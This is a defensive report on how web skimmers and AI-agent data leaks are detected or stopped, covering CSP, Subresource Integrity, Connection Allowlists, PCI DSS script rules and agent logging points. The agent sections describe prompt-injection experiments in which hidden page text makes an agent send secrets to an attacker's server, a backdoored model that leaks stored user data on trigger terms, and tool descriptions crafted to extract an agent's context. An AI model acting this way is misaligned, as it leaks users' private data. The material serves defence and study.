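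The published rates imply that the altered test set contained about 1,497 scripts, of which 63, or about one in 24, were malicious. Skimmers are presumably much rarer among the scripts that run on ordinary shopping sites. A classifier's precision falls as skimmers become rarer, even if its recall and its rate of false alarms on benign scripts stay the same.

If the main test had the same proportion of malicious scripts, the support vector machine wrongly flagged about 0.21% of benign ones. Applied to a million scripts, those rates give:

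| Share of scripts that are skimmers | Skimmers found | False alarms | Share of alarms that are correct |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 24, as in the test | about 40,500 | about 2,000 | 95% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 962 | about 2,100 | 31% |
| 1 in 10,000 | 96 | about 2,100 | 4% |

The last two rows are illustrations, since the true share is unknown. A security company that scans thousands of shops would need another check to sort the alarms, such as whether the script sends data to an unfamiliar domain. A single shop could manage more easily, as it would have about 38 false alarms a year if it had 50 scripts that all changed every day and errors occurred independently. It could reduce the work further by examining only new or changed scripts on its payment page, where card industry rules already require it to control scripts.

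Accuracy, the share of all scripts classified correctly, conceals this problem. Because most scripts were benign, the decision tree was 95% accurate on the altered data without finding any malicious scripts.

Skimmers also change, and criminals sell them as kits. Pereira and colleagues mention one kit that sold for $1,500 and compromised more than 480 websites in early 2024. If copies of one kit appear in both the training data and the test data, a high score may only show that the classifier recognises that kit. Training on older skimmers and testing on ones that appeared later would give a better estimate of how well the classifier detects new ones. The paper describes no such test and no trial on live shops.

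The logs cover the checkout, unlike data from a crawler that visits only home pages. To achieve similar results, a shop would have to collect the same kind of log from real customers' browsers or from regular test purchases. Pereira and colleagues leave a lightweight version for live use to future work. An outside scanner that reaches the payment page in only half of the shops it visits will miss about half of the skimmers that run only on that page, even with a perfect classifier.

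## Controlling which scripts run and where a page can connect

A skimmer classifier examines scripts that have already run, but a site's owner can also tell the browser in advance which scripts may run and which servers the page may contact. The browser applies these rules during every visit, including at the checkout, which outside scanners often fail to reach. When a script breaks a rule, the browser can block the action and report the attempt to the owner.

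### Content Security Policy

A Content Security Policy (CSP) is a set of such rules in a header, which is information that a web server sends along with a page. A shop that uses a chat service and a payment provider might send this one, spread here over several lines:

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  script-src 'self' https://chat.example;
  connect-src 'self' https://chat.example https://pay.example;
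  report-to security
```

The script-src rule allows script files from the shop's own origin ('self') and from the chat service. The browser blocks files from anywhere else. It also blocks inline scripts, which are written directly into the page's text, because an attacker who can insert text into a page could otherwise insert a script. The shop can exempt its own inline scripts with a nonce, a new random value that the server generates for each page it sends. The server puts the nonce in the header and in the tags of its own scripts, and the browser runs the scripts that carry it.

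The connect-src rule limits where scripts can send data through fetch, XHR, beacons and WebSockets, but other routes need their own rules. The sample doesn't restrict images, for example, so a script could still send data in an image request to any server. The shop could add img-src, or default-src, which applies to most types of request that have no separate rule. Default-src does not cover form submissions, which need form-action. CSP has no rule that stops a script from sending the visitor to a new page. An owner who forgets a rule may never notice, because the page still works normally.

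Lists of script sources are also hard to maintain because a tag manager adds scripts from addresses that the site owner may not know in advance. The strict-dynamic option solves this by letting approved scripts load others, but whoever controls the tag manager then chooses which scripts it loads. According to Chrome's *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026), sites often adopt broad policies because CSP is difficult to manage, and these policies can allow unauthorised connections.

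The browser's violation reports include the page, the blocked address and the rule, and often the file and line of the script responsible. If a skimmer uses fetch to send card numbers to a server the policy doesn't allow, the first customer whose browser enforces the policy triggers a report. A second header, Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only, applies the same rules without blocking anything, so a site owner can use CSP only for detection. Someone still has to sort the reports, because extensions in visitors' browsers can trigger them too.

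### Subresource Integrity

The sample policy controls where a script comes from but not what it contains. If someone alters a file on chat.example, the browser will still run it. Subresource Integrity (SRI) fixes the content instead. The site's owner puts a hash of the approved file into the tag that loads it:

```
<script src="https://cdn.example/charts-4.2.1.js"
        integrity="sha384-Kx7v…"
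        crossorigin="anonymous"></script>
```

A complete hash of this type has 64 characters, but the sample shows only four. The browser downloads the file, computes its hash and runs the script only if the two hashes match. Changing a single character of the file changes the hash. The crossorigin attribute makes the browser ask the other server for permission to read the file, and without that permission the script does not run.

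SRI protects against an attacker who controls the supplier's server, because the approved hash is in the site's own page. It suits files that never change, such as a library with its version number in the address. Suppliers of tag managers, advertising scripts and session replay often update a file without changing its address. When they do, the hash no longer matches, so browsers block the script on every site that still lists the old hash. A site can avoid this by hosting its own copy, but then it has to install the supplier's updates itself.

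The browser checks only the file named in the tag. If that script loads another, the browser checks the second only if the first supplies a hash for it. A hash also cannot show whether the approved file was harmless.

SRI is a weak detector because the browser does not report a failed hash check to the site owner. It only writes an error to the visitor's console, so the owner may first hear about the problem from a customer who cannot see a chart.

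### Connection Allowlists

A Connection Allowlist is a newer header that lists all the destinations a page may contact. The browser refuses every other connection, whichever script or part of the page starts it:

```
Connection-Allowlist:
  (response-origin "https://pay.example/v1/*" "https://*.chat.example");
  report-to=security
```

The token response-origin stands for the shop's own origin. The other entries allow addresses under /v1/ at the payment provider and any subdomain of the chat service.

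West argues in *Connection Allowlists*, a draft specification he edits at Google, that CSP is the wrong tool for controlling where a page can connect because it sorts requests by type. A leak through a font request does as much harm as one through an image request. CSP also does not cover some connections, such as early lookups of a host's address and WebRTC, which video calls use.

The more important difference between CSP and a connection allowlist is that a forgotten CSP rule leaves a route open, while a service missing from the allowlist stops working. Report URI's *Connection Allowlist*, documentation from a company that collects browser reports for websites, instead presents control over paths as the main practical difference. This overstates the contrast, since a CSP rule can also name a path, although the browser ignores the path after a redirect.

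Redirects and WebRTC have stricter defaults. Helme, whose company runs Report URI, explains that checking the original address is not enough because a permitted server can redirect the request elsewhere. The browser therefore blocks redirects unless the header includes redirects=allow. Report URI describes this as blocking redirects to destinations not on the list, but Chromium's own tests, which appear in Mozilla's *Sync PR 59539*, check that the browser refuses even a redirect from the page's own origin back to itself. Some pages will probably break on a shop's site if it uses redirects internally.

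The list cannot describe WebRTC destinations, because browsers find each other's addresses while they set up the connection. The header therefore has a single setting that allows or blocks all WebRTC connections, and blocking is the default. To enforce a block, Chrome stops the page from creating a WebRTC connection, and a separate part of the browser also refuses the network access in case an attacker has taken over the process that runs the page.

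These strict rules have side effects. The list applies to navigation, so ordinary links to websites that are not on it fail. That would be unworkable for a news site, but a checkout page rarely needs to link elsewhere. Sign-in can also fail. Chrome's *FedCM* (2026), a notice about the browser's system for signing in through another company, tells sites to add that company's addresses to their lists.

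A mistake in the header can also remove the protection. Under West's draft, if the owner leaves out the parentheses around the list, the browser discards the header and the page can connect anywhere. If the browser cannot interpret an entry in the list, it skips that entry, which makes the list stricter. Chrome's developer tools display such errors.

Connection Allowlists also have a report-only version. Each report contains the page, the unlisted destination, the allowlist, and whether the browser blocked the connection or only recorded it. Unlike many CSP reports, those in West's draft do not identify the script responsible, so the site owner cannot tell from them what tried to connect. CentralCSP, another company that processes browser reports, warned during the trial that the fields could still change.

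Report URI stores only one in ten of these reports by default, so that a badly written list doesn't flood the owner's account. If it chooses them at random, the chance that it has stored at least one report of a skimmer is 10% after one attempt, 65% after ten and 99% after 44. A shop with three sales a day would take about two weeks to reach 44.

### From trial to release

Google tested the feature in an origin trial, which lets websites register to use an experimental feature with real visitors. Sharma first planned the trial for Chrome 147 to 150, then moved it to Chrome 148 to 151. It initially covered ordinary requests, navigation and redirects, with WebRTC and WebSockets to be added later. In June, West (2026) wrote that the implementation was nearly ready and that feedback from developers was relatively positive. They had asked for more features but raised no basic objections.

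Chrome (2026) included Connection Allowlists in version 152, released on 25 August. Sites no longer have to register. The release covers Android, ChromeOS, Linux, macOS and Windows, but not Chrome on iPhones. Microsoft also ran a trial for its Chromium-based Edge browser, which expired on 8 September 2026 according to Microsoft's *Connection Allowlists*.

Firefox and Safari ignore the header. In February, West noted that neither Mozilla nor Apple had formally replied to his requests for their views, and in March, Sharma reported no signal from either. A Mozilla record marked "fixed" for Firefox 152 means only that Mozilla copied Chromium's tests for the feature into Firefox's code. Firefox failed the tests that expect it to block a connection.

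A shop that sends the header therefore protects only some of its customers. However, a report from one Chrome user may lead the owner to remove a skimmer that also affects customers with iPhones.

### Two attacks in March 2026

Sansec's *Novel WebRTC skimmer bypasses security controls at $100+ billion car maker* (2026) describes a payment skimmer that used WebRTC instead of web requests to load code and send out stolen payment data. Sansec, which sells security software for online shops, had not seen a skimmer do this before. A small script in the page opened a WebRTC connection to the attackers' server, received the rest of the skimmer, and added it to the page, reusing the nonce of one of the site's own scripts if there was one. Sansec thinks the attackers most likely got in through PolyShell, a flaw that lets anyone upload files to a vulnerable shop.

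The other attack involved AppsFlyer, a company that measures which advertisements lead people to install apps. Its customers load a script from websdk.appsflyer.com. According to AppsFlyer's *March 10th, 2026 Incident*, traffic for that address went to attacker-controlled servers from about 00:31 to 09:47 UTC, and some visitors received an altered script. AppsFlyer had noticed a problem at 00:22 but took more than nine hours to fix it.

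cside's *AppsFlyer Web SDK supply-chain compromise* (2026) explains that the attackers had taken over AppsFlyer's account with its domain registrar, the company through which it registers its domain name, and never touched AppsFlyer's own servers. Reflectiz's *AppsFlyer SDK Exploited in New Supply Chain Crypto Attack* instead places the altered file on AppsFlyer's own delivery network and gives a window of 48 hours. AppsFlyer's and cside's accounts of the method agree with each other, so they are more credible on that point. The length of the window is less certain. Networks keep copies of domain records for a time, so some visitors may have received the altered script after AppsFlyer had regained control.

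Reflectiz reports that the altered script still did its normal work but replaced the cryptocurrency wallet addresses that visitors typed with the attackers' own. It also sent out page addresses, times and details of the visitor's browser.

| Control | WebRTC skimmer | Altered AppsFlyer script |
|---|---|---|
| CSP, script-src | Failed to stop the second part of the skimmer where the site used nonces | Would have allowed the script, which came from an approved domain |
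| CSP, connect-src | Does not apply to WebRTC | Would have allowed data sent to AppsFlyer's domain, and blocked and reported data sent to an unlisted one |
| Subresource Integrity | Little use if the attackers could change the shop's own pages | Would have stopped the script on any site with a hash for the file |
| Connection Allowlists | Would have blocked the WebRTC connection in a browser that supports the header | The same as connect-src |

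A Connection Allowlist with the default settings would have stopped the second part of the WebRTC skimmer from arriving. However, Chrome released the feature five months after the attack, and the trial did not cover WebRTC at first. Attackers who can write to a shop's server may also be able to remove its headers. Sansec mentions an experimental CSP rule for WebRTC in Chrome but says almost no site uses it.

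Monitoring inside the page could also have detected the skimmer, because a wrapper or an engine log can record that a script created a WebRTC connection. A tool that inspects web requests would have missed the traffic, since WebRTC traffic is encrypted and does not use HTTP. Very few checkouts offer video calls, so an alarm for any use of WebRTC on a payment page would rarely be false.

Reflectiz contradicts itself about whether SRI would have stopped the AppsFlyer script. In its article, it lists SRI among the defences that failed, because the attackers changed the file at its source, but in its FAQ it says that a hash would have blocked the file. The FAQ is correct, because the browser checks the file against the hash in the customer's page, not against another copy from AppsFlyer. However, a site could have used a hash only if AppsFlyer offered an unchanging version of the file.

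Limits on connections would have done little to protect visitors who typed a wallet address, because the altered script did not have to send the address anywhere. The visitor submitted the form as usual, and the site received the attackers' address instead of the intended one. To detect this, a site would have to notice that the script had changed or that it wrote to a field it did not need to change.

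AppsFlyer cannot tell what the script did in visitors' browsers, and has advised its customers to search their own logs. Reflectiz claims its monitoring service would have raised an alert within hours, but gives no evidence from a customer that used AppsFlyer at the time.

### When the destination is on the list

Neither connect-src nor a Connection Allowlist stops an attacker who can receive data at a permitted address. In the AppsFlyer attack, the permitted domain itself led to the attackers' servers. West's draft acknowledges that an allowlist relies on names leading to the right servers, and recommends permitting only encrypted connections, since a server then needs a certificate for the name. This helps less when attackers control the domain's DNS records, because they can usually obtain a valid certificate.

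Shared services cause a similar problem without any hijacking. All the customers of an analytics company may send data to the same address, and an account number in each request identifies the customer. If a shop permits that address, the browser will also let a malicious script send data to a criminal's account with the same company.

An honest recipient can also receive too much, as Yandex did when its recorder collected passwords. A site with an allowlist would have had to include Yandex for the recorder to work, so the allowlist would not have blocked the passwords. An allowlist also doesn't block data that a site's own server forwards to a tracker.

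A Connection Allowlist applies only to the page it came with, and West notes that another page of the same origin may have a looser list or none. In *Intent to Prototype*, a proposal from Microsoft, Maslen warns that a page with a strict list can also pass data to an embedded frame that has no list, and the frame can send it on. He proposes letting a page require a list from every frame it embeds, including nested frames. The browser would not load a frame that did not agree. The proposal had no release date when he made it.

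An owner can reduce these risks by keeping the list short and making it strictest on the pages that handle the most sensitive data.

### The payment card rules

Businesses that accept cards must follow the Payment Card Industry Data Security Standard (PCI DSS), which the card companies enforce through contracts. Two requirements in the current version, 4.0.1, concern scripts on payment pages and have been mandatory since 31 March 2025.

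Requirement 6.4.3 applies to every script that a payment page loads and runs in the customer's browser. The business must:

- have a method to confirm that each script is authorised
- have a method to assure the integrity of each script
- keep an inventory of the scripts, with a written justification for each.

Requirement 11.6.1 calls for a mechanism that alerts staff to unauthorised changes to the page's scripts and security-related headers, as the customer's browser receives them. The mechanism must run at least once a week, unless the business justifies another frequency in a formal risk analysis. Checking the headers matters because an intruder who removes a CSP or a Connection Allowlist also stops the reports that would have revealed the theft.

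The standard lets businesses choose their methods. CSP can help control which scripts the page loads, and SRI can check the integrity of files that do not change. For other files, a business needs a tool to compare each version with the previous one and a person to decide whether each change is legitimate. If a supplier updates its script daily, that person is likely to start approving changes without reading them.

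Weekly checks are too infrequent to catch attacks this short reliably. By AppsFlyer's account, its altered script was available for about nine and a quarter hours. A weekly check at a random time would have had about a 5.5% chance of falling within that period, and a daily check about 39%. Reflectiz puts the window at 48 hours, which would raise the weekly check's chance to about 29%.

A skimmer that stays on the site is easier to catch, but if it appears at a random time between weekly checks, it still runs for an average of three and a half days before the next one. In a shop with 1,000 card payments a day, that is enough time to copy about 3,500 cards. Continuous reports from customers' browsers would shorten the delay, and the standard does not prohibit them.

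The rules also miss some transmissions entirely:

- They cover payment pages, so a script that collects health details from a booking form is outside them.
- They control which scripts are present, but neither requirement limits where those scripts may send data.
- A session replay script with a written justification can pass every check and still record a card number, because its code has not changed.
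- A checking tool that visits the page itself examines the copy it receives, which may differ from the one a customer receives.

An inventory can also be incomplete. If a shop is a single-page application, the inventory has to include every script that a customer could have loaded earlier in the visit.

### Keeping data out of scripts' reach

The controls described so far leave sensitive data where a permitted script can read them. A site can instead put the most sensitive fields somewhere that its scripts cannot reach. For payments, the usual method is to load the card fields in a frame from the payment provider's domain. The shop can have one frame for the whole form or a separate one for each field, which makes it easier to keep the shop's own design. A payment then works as follows:

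1. The customer types the card number into the provider's frame, out of reach of the shop's scripts.
2. When the customer clicks the payment button, the shop's script sends the frame a message asking it to continue.
3. The frame sends the card number directly to the provider, which returns a token, a substitute value that normally works only for that shop.
4. The shop's server uses the token to request the payment.

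A skimmer in the shop's page could take the token, but a thief could do little with it. The shop also never holds the card number, so someone who breaks into its database cannot steal card numbers from it.

A script in the surrounding page can still show a false form, so the card industry's rules on scripts also cover pages that embed a provider's frame, while the provider is responsible for the scripts inside it. In 2025 the standard's publisher relaxed this for small businesses that leave all card handling to others and use its shortest self-assessment form. They no longer have to report on the two requirements, but they must confirm that scripts cannot be used to attack their site. CSP can limit which frames a page may load, but it cannot prevent an approved script from drawing a form in the page itself.

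Passwords need a different method because the site has to receive them. Gautam and colleagues modified Firefox to replace a false password with the real one as the request leaves the browser. Unlike a payment frame, this requires no changes from site owners.

Swapping the password also avoids a weakness of allowlists, which let an approved destination receive any data. The modified browser checks the destination before sending the real password, so a session replay service on the site's allowlist still receives only the false one. A unique false password could also serve as a canary string, since finding it in a request to any other company would show that a script had read the field.

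The method depends on the visitor using such a browser. Payment frames usually cover only the card details, so every script on the page can still read the customer's name, address and email.

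## What an AI agent's logs record and what they miss

A browser that enforces a Connection Allowlist can tell the site's owner about every forbidden connection. AI agents have no single program that handles all their connections. The host passes on tool calls, tool servers act on them, and other programs on the machine may open their own connections. Each can keep a log, and a leak that is obvious in one log may not appear in another.

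An organisation can observe an agent at six points: the final answer, the host's log of tool calls, a gateway between the host and the tool servers, the machine's processes, the network, and the tool provider's own systems. Logs made closer to the model are better evidence of why the agent sent something but weaker evidence of where the data went.

### The final answer

A useful record of an agent's answer includes its full text, the time, the session, the model's name and version, and the address of every image and link, since an address can carry data. According to Lan and colleagues, most safety evaluations of language models examine only the text of the response.

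Their experiment with hidden instructions in web pages measured how much such a check misses. The agent ran on a version of the Qwen 2.5 model with 7 billion parameters (the numbers a model learns in training), which is small by current standards. The researchers put the instructions in the page's title, description, body or link text. The agent reached the page either directly or through redirects, and the instructions asked for the secret either whole or in four pieces. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

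The agent sent data to the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1%). The 89% in the paper's abstract is the rate for pages reached through redirects. The final answer looked harmless in about 402 of the 423 runs. The user asked only for a summary, so a normal answer would not mention the request to the attacker's server.

Agents sometimes mention a transmission. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos* (2026) describes a leak that researchers at Glow Labs named PixelLeak. Developers had asked coding agents to prove that user interface changes worked. GitHub, a site where programmers store and review code, accepts images for code reviews only through the browser, but the agents worked from the command line. Some therefore posted their screenshots in public repositories, which are project folders that anyone can open. Glow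 Labs found more than 13,000 internal images from over 300 organisations, including customers' billing records.

When the researchers reproduced the behaviour with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, the agent wrote that it had "created a new public repo" for the screenshots. A developer who read this could have deleted the repository at once, but if the agent works unattended, there may be nobody to read the message.

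### The tool-call log

The host can log every tool call. An entry for an email might look like this:

```
time         2025-09-18 09:14:22
session      4f1c, turn 6
user         anna
server       postmark-mcp, version 1.0.16
tool         send_email
arguments    to: sam@client.example
             subject: Invoice 2071
             text: Dear Sam, the invoice for August is ...
result       "Email sent"
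approval     automatic, under a standing rule
read before  invoice 2071 (turn 4), customer list (turn 5)
```

The last line shows what was in the context when the model wrote the call. If the text of this email contained other customers' names, a reviewer could trace them to the customer list.

The arguments are the most valuable field in a tool-call log, since they are normally the only part of the conversation a tool sees. *ContextLeak* (Jia, Wang and colleagues, 2026) therefore divides a theft by a malicious tool into three steps: the agent selects the tool, the agent puts its context into the arguments, and the tool sends the arguments to the attacker. A tool-call log covers the first two steps. If a weather tool receives the user's whole conversation, a log with full arguments contains the evidence, but a log with only the tool's name shows an ordinary weather request.

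An agent can also leak data through a series of calls that each look normal. Zhang and Pei (2026), in *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*, describe an attack in which someone publishes an altered model that behaves normally until a user's question contains certain terms, for example from medicine or video streaming. The model then looks up what the assistant has stored about the user, as helpful assistants often do, and makes a web request that resembles a search but contains the stored details in encoded form. The log contains both calls, but a reviewer needs their order and the complete web address to connect them.

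Lan and colleagues tested how splitting a secret across several requests affects detection. When the instructions asked for the whole secret at once, the first request contained recognisable sensitive data in 96.7% of runs. When they asked for it in four pieces, the share fell to 26.3%. A filter that examines each request separately would miss many of these pieces, because a few characters look like ordinary usage data.

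Part of the fall occurred because the small model often failed to carry out the longer instructions. It contacted the attacker's server in 77% of the runs with a split secret, compared with 99% of the others. The paper also reports a lower rate of recognisable data in the first three requests (15.8%) than in the first request alone. This is impossible under its own definition, because any run that counts for the first request must also count for the first three. The 73% figure is therefore reasonable evidence that splitting a secret weakens checks on single requests, but not of how much. The paper's tables do not give the share of runs in which all four pieces arrived, so it is unclear how often the attacker would have obtained the complete secret.

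A session number in each log entry makes it easier to find data that was split across several requests. Four short requests from one session to the same unfamiliar server within a minute are suspicious together, even if none contains a recognisable key.

The tool-call log omits requests that the host makes by itself, such as the page preview in this experiment, and requests to load images in an answer. The log records any shell command the agent runs, but if the command starts a script, the log may contain little more than the script's name.

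### A gateway between agents and tool servers

Each host keeps its log in its own format, often on an employee's laptop, where the employee or the agent may be able to change it. An organisation can instead require its agents to reach all tool servers through a gateway, a server that forwards the calls and records them all in one log.

A gateway can log the arguments and results of each call, which employee and which agent made it, the credentials used, the tool server's address, and whether the gateway allowed the call. It can also save each tool's description whenever the server sends it. If an agent starts to behave oddly, someone can then check whether a supplier changed a description beforehand.

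The gateway does not normally receive the user's conversation with the agent, so it can log that the agent sent a dental record to an insurer, but not that the user had asked it to send only a date. To judge whether the transmission was authorised, a reviewer also needs the host's log, with a session number that appears in both logs.

The gateway logs only what passes through it. A host can bypass it by starting a tool server on the user's machine and communicating with that server directly. Built-in tools and shell commands also bypass it. OWASP, a software security non-profit, lists missing audit logs and unapproved tool servers separately among the main MCP risks, according to the summary in mcp.directory's *MCP Security 2026*. To find unapproved servers, the summary recommends inventorying the programs on employees' machines and logging the network addresses those machines look up or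 contact.

PixelLeak also happened outside what the affected companies usually monitor. At a manufacturer with more than 100,000 employees, an agent tasked with checking a billing screen created a public repository in the developer's personal GitHub account. According to Help Net Security, the security team did not notice because the agent ran on the employee's laptop, outside the company's GitHub organisation. The images were still online when Glow Labs contacted the company.

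### The machine's processes

A process is a running program. Monitoring software on the machine can log each process's name, full command, user and start time, the files it opens, the connections it makes, and the parent process that started it. The parent is important because a developer and an agent can run the same upload command. If the parent is the agent's host process, the agent probably ran the command.

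A process log can fill gaps in the host's log. If an agent starts a script that opens a file of access keys and then contacts an outside server, the host may have recorded only the script's name, while the process log shows the file and the connection. It also covers local tool servers, because they are ordinary programs. About a third of the organisations affected by PixelLeak had developers who ran gitshot, an open-source tool that publishes screenshots for code reviews. Searching process logs for "gitshot" would have found many of them.

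Process logs do not show why the agent ran a program, and they usually do not show what the program sent, because programs encrypt data before sending it. They cannot record the activity of a tool server on another company's machine. If the agent runs in its supplier's cloud, the customer may have no process log at all.

Monitoring software also has trouble identifying abnormal behaviour. A text editor that opened hundreds of files, started a shell and contacted several new websites would look like an intrusion, but a coding agent does all this on a normal day. Techzine's *Rapid adoption of AI agents exposes structural weakness in MCP* reported in early 2026 that existing detection tools typically treat MCP processes as legitimate and raise no alarm.

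### The network

A network log can record the time of a connection, the machine that made it, the destination's name and IP address, and the amount of data sent each way. If the organisation decrypts its traffic for inspection, the log can also include full web addresses and the contents of requests. Otherwise, it can show that a laptop sent 40 kilobytes to a server but not what the data contained.

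Network logs record requests that never appear as tool calls, such as those the host makes to fetch previews. Lan and colleagues measured attack success by the requests that reached the attacker's server. In 120 runs on harmless pages, the agent never contacted that server, and they conclude that outgoing traffic is a clear signal with no false positives.

The conclusion holds in the experiment because the researchers knew which server belonged to the attacker. A company's security team would have to pick out the attacker's server from a list of all the servers its agents contacted, and an agent researching a topic on the web may contact dozens of unfamiliar ones in an hour. The 0% false positive rate therefore does not estimate how often a network monitor would raise false alarms in a real organisation.

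Leaks to familiar destinations, by contrast, can look like normal work. In PixelLeak, the images went to GitHub, which the companies' developers use all day. Glow Labs found that 93% of the cases involved repositories under employees' own usernames. A network log that records only the destination's name shows the same entry for an upload to the company's private repository and an upload to a public one. Searching decrypted traffic for text patterns would also have missed the billing records, because they were in images.

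### Defences in the Silent Egress experiment

Lan and colleagues also compared several defences, with 30 runs each. They used only the simplest version of the attack, with the instructions in the page's body and the secret sent whole.

| Defence | Runs in which the agent tried to send data | Runs in which data got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 30 |
| A warning in the developer's instructions | 20 | 20 |
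| Tags around web content that mark it as untrusted | 30 | 30 |
| The warning and the tags | 17 | 17 |
| A list of permitted domains | 30 | 0 |
| A filter for suspicious addresses | 25 | 0 |
| A filter for words such as "password" in the address | 7 | 0 |
| A filter for random-looking values in the address | 0 | 0 |
| All of these together | 0 | 0 |

The warning and the tags work only if the model follows them. The tags had no effect, and the difference between 20 and 17 runs could be chance. The list of permitted domains stopped every attempt because the attacker's domain was not on it and the software making the request checked the list regardless of what the model wrote.

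The results for the other filters are less reliable. The filter for suspicious addresses blocks addresses whose path contains words such as "collect". The attack's address contained that word, so the test favoured this filter. The word filter caught seven requests, but no data got out in the other 23 runs either. Without a defence, every run leaked data. The researchers suggest that the model sometimes encoded or reformatted the secret, which would explain why the filter missed it but not why no data got out.

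The filter for random-looking values has a similar problem. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids writing such values when the filter is active, but a filter that checks finished requests cannot affect what the model writes unless the host tells the model about it. The filter's threshold was 4 on a standard scale of randomness, and the sample key printed in the paper scores about 3.85, so the filter would have let that key through if the tests used it. Another team would have to repeat these tests before anyone relied on the zeros.

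The researchers acknowledge that their set-up favoured the attacker. They placed the secret in the agent's context, gave the agent few instructions beyond the format for tool calls, and had the host pass on the page's text without cleaning it. No person had to approve a request. A commercial agent usually has longer instructions, and its developer may have trained the model to resist injected text. However, Lan and colleagues argue that larger models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably, though the study did not test this.

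Answer checks failed and the domain list worked, and both results should apply more widely because neither depends on the model's skill. The experiment covered only ordinary web requests, so it provides no evidence about other routes, such as address lookups.

### The tool provider's own systems

Jia and colleagues' third step, in which the tool sends the data on, happens inside the tool server. The host's log ends with the server's reply, and the server controls what that reply contains. A complete record of what the server did would include the data it received, the files it stored, every outside service it contacted, and, for an email, every recipient. Only the provider can keep such a record, and customers see only what the provider chooses to show them.

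The Hacker News (2025) reported on what researchers described as the first malicious MCP server found in actual use. Postmark, a service that sends email for other companies' software, offers an official library that lets AI assistants send email. Someone using the name "phanpak" copied it and published the copy as postmark-mcp on npm, a public collection of JavaScript packages. According to Koi, the security company that discovered the theft, versions 1.0.0 to 1.0.15 worked as they should. Version 1.0.16, released on 17 September 2025, added one line of code that sent a blind copy of every email to phanpak's address.

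The sample log entry above is what a host could have recorded for such an email. Every field in it is correct. Assuming that the server ran on the user's machine, the six observation points would have held the following:

| Observation point | Record of the email to Sam |
|---|---|
| Final answer | Confirmation that the agent sent the invoice |
| Tool-call log | The correct recipient, subject and text |
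| Gateway | Nothing, because the host contacted the server directly |
| Processes | The tool server, connecting to Postmark as usual |
| Network | An encrypted connection to Postmark |
| Postmark's email log | Sam's address and the blind-copy address |

A list of permitted destinations would not have stopped the blind copies to the attacker, because the server needed access to Postmark and Postmark delivered them. Snyk's security advisory *Malicious Package Affecting postmark-mcp package, versions >=1.0.16* (2025) recommends that users search their email logs for blind copies to the attacker's domain. ITPro's *A malicious MCP server is silently stealing user emails* quotes Koi's co-founder Idan Dardikman as saying that such servers bypass "every security control from DLP to email gateways". That may be true of the controls on the user's side, but Postmark's log still held evidence of the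 copies.

Nobody knows how many emails the developer obtained. Expert Insights' *AI-Assistant MCP Downloaded 1,500 Times Per Week Found Stealing Emails* reports Koi's estimate of 3,000 to 15,000, based on weekly downloads, and adds that the true number may be smaller. Paubox, an email company, puts total downloads at 1,643. If both download figures are right, nearly all the downloads happened in about a week. Neither is a count of users, since one person can download a package many times and never send an email with it.

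The developer deleted the package after Koi made contact, but copies already installed kept working and kept sending blind copies of emails. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), an entry in a public database of malicious packages, lists 1.0.16 as the version in which the theft began. A company whose tool-call logs include version numbers could find every affected email with one search.

Other misuse appears only in a provider's logs because it doesn't involve the user's agent. Techzine describes a scan that found 1,862 MCP servers on the internet with no login requirement. An outsider could call these servers and reach the same data as the agent they served, and the agent's host would have no record of the calls.

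### Scanning tool servers before use

Logs cannot show what a server does internally, so an organisation may want to examine a server before connecting an agent to it. Scanners read either the server's tool descriptions or its code.

Scanning descriptions would not have exposed postmark-mcp, because the only change was in the code. Scanning also depends on recognising suspicious wording. Jia and colleagues trained a language model to write tool names and descriptions that lead an agent to hand over its context. The descriptions present this information as something the tool needs to work correctly, without openly instructing the agent to hand it over. Jia and colleagues report that existing detectors were insufficient against these tools. Training models to avoid malicious tools did not solve the problem either, and often made the models worse at choosing harmless ones.

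Scanning code can work, as when Koi's software flagged postmark-mcp as suspicious. Separating real problems from false alarms across thousands of servers is harder. Trend Micro's *Hunt Them All* used a language model to search the code of 19,000 MCP servers, and the model reported 17,558 vulnerabilities. A second pass by the same model removed obvious errors and left just over 15,000. The researchers then gave a random sample of 2,287 to a different model, which upheld 438, or about one in five. Those 438 still needed human review, and the second model may also have rejected some genuine vulnerabilities. The scan looked for programming mistakes rather than deliberate theft, but a scanner for theft faces the same difficulty.

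*MCP server security scores are review prompts, not verdicts* (Schipper, 2026) describes a July study that ran existing scanners on 64,611 servers. The scanners rated 96.89% of the servers as risky, and the researchers concluded that these signals were unreliable. Schipper's own scanner puts 63% of servers in its lowest risk band. A scanner that rates nearly every server as risky is little help in choosing between two of them.

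Code scanning also requires access to the code. Anyone can read a package like postmark-mcp, which users install on their own machines. A remote server, however, runs on its provider's machine, and the provider can publish one program and run another. The Hacker News' *Welcome to the Jungle* (2026), by the security company OX Security, makes this point about the public MCP servers OX surveyed. OX found that the marketplaces it examined did not review servers before listing them.

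The survey covered 15,465 listed servers from five registries. Many were duplicates or shared a host, which left 5,095 different host names:

- 15.6% of the host names, or about 795, led to machines outside the United States, including 19 in China and 18 in Russia.
- 2.3%, or about 117, no longer led anywhere. Six of these were on expired domains that anyone could register for $4 to $12 a year.
- 0.45%, or about 23, led through services that connect a personal computer to the internet, so the server was probably running in someone's home.

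These figures cover only where the servers are, and OX did not report that any of them had misused the data they received. A location outside the United States is not a problem in itself, for example when a German company uses a German server. The expired domains are few, but they are the most serious finding for anyone who relies on logs. If a stranger registered one of them, agents still set up to use that server would send their calls to the stranger, and the host's log would show the same server name as before. A log that also records the server's IP address or the owner of its security certificate could reveal the change, or show that a server has moved to another country since the customer approved it.

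### Data sent to the model provider

When an agent reads a file, the tool-call log records a file read with no outside recipient, even if the model runs remotely and the host sends the file's contents to the model provider with the next turn.

*'I leaked secrets'* (Udinmwen, 2026) reports a case from a security vendor in which an AI coding assistant exposed sensitive data without an attacker being involved. During a routine code review, the assistant could not find its configuration file, so it collected all of the computer's environment variables, which are settings that programs share and that often include passwords. Over ten sessions, it repeatedly read whole configuration files and exposed working passwords for live systems and access tokens for human resources software. It did not remember warnings between sessions, so it made the same mistake again.

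The employer's rules and its contract with the model provider determine whether this was unauthorised. Even if the provider protects the data, the passwords are now in another company's systems, so the employer would be wise to change them. Sending the whole file was oversharing even if it was authorised, because a code review rarely requires the actual passwords.

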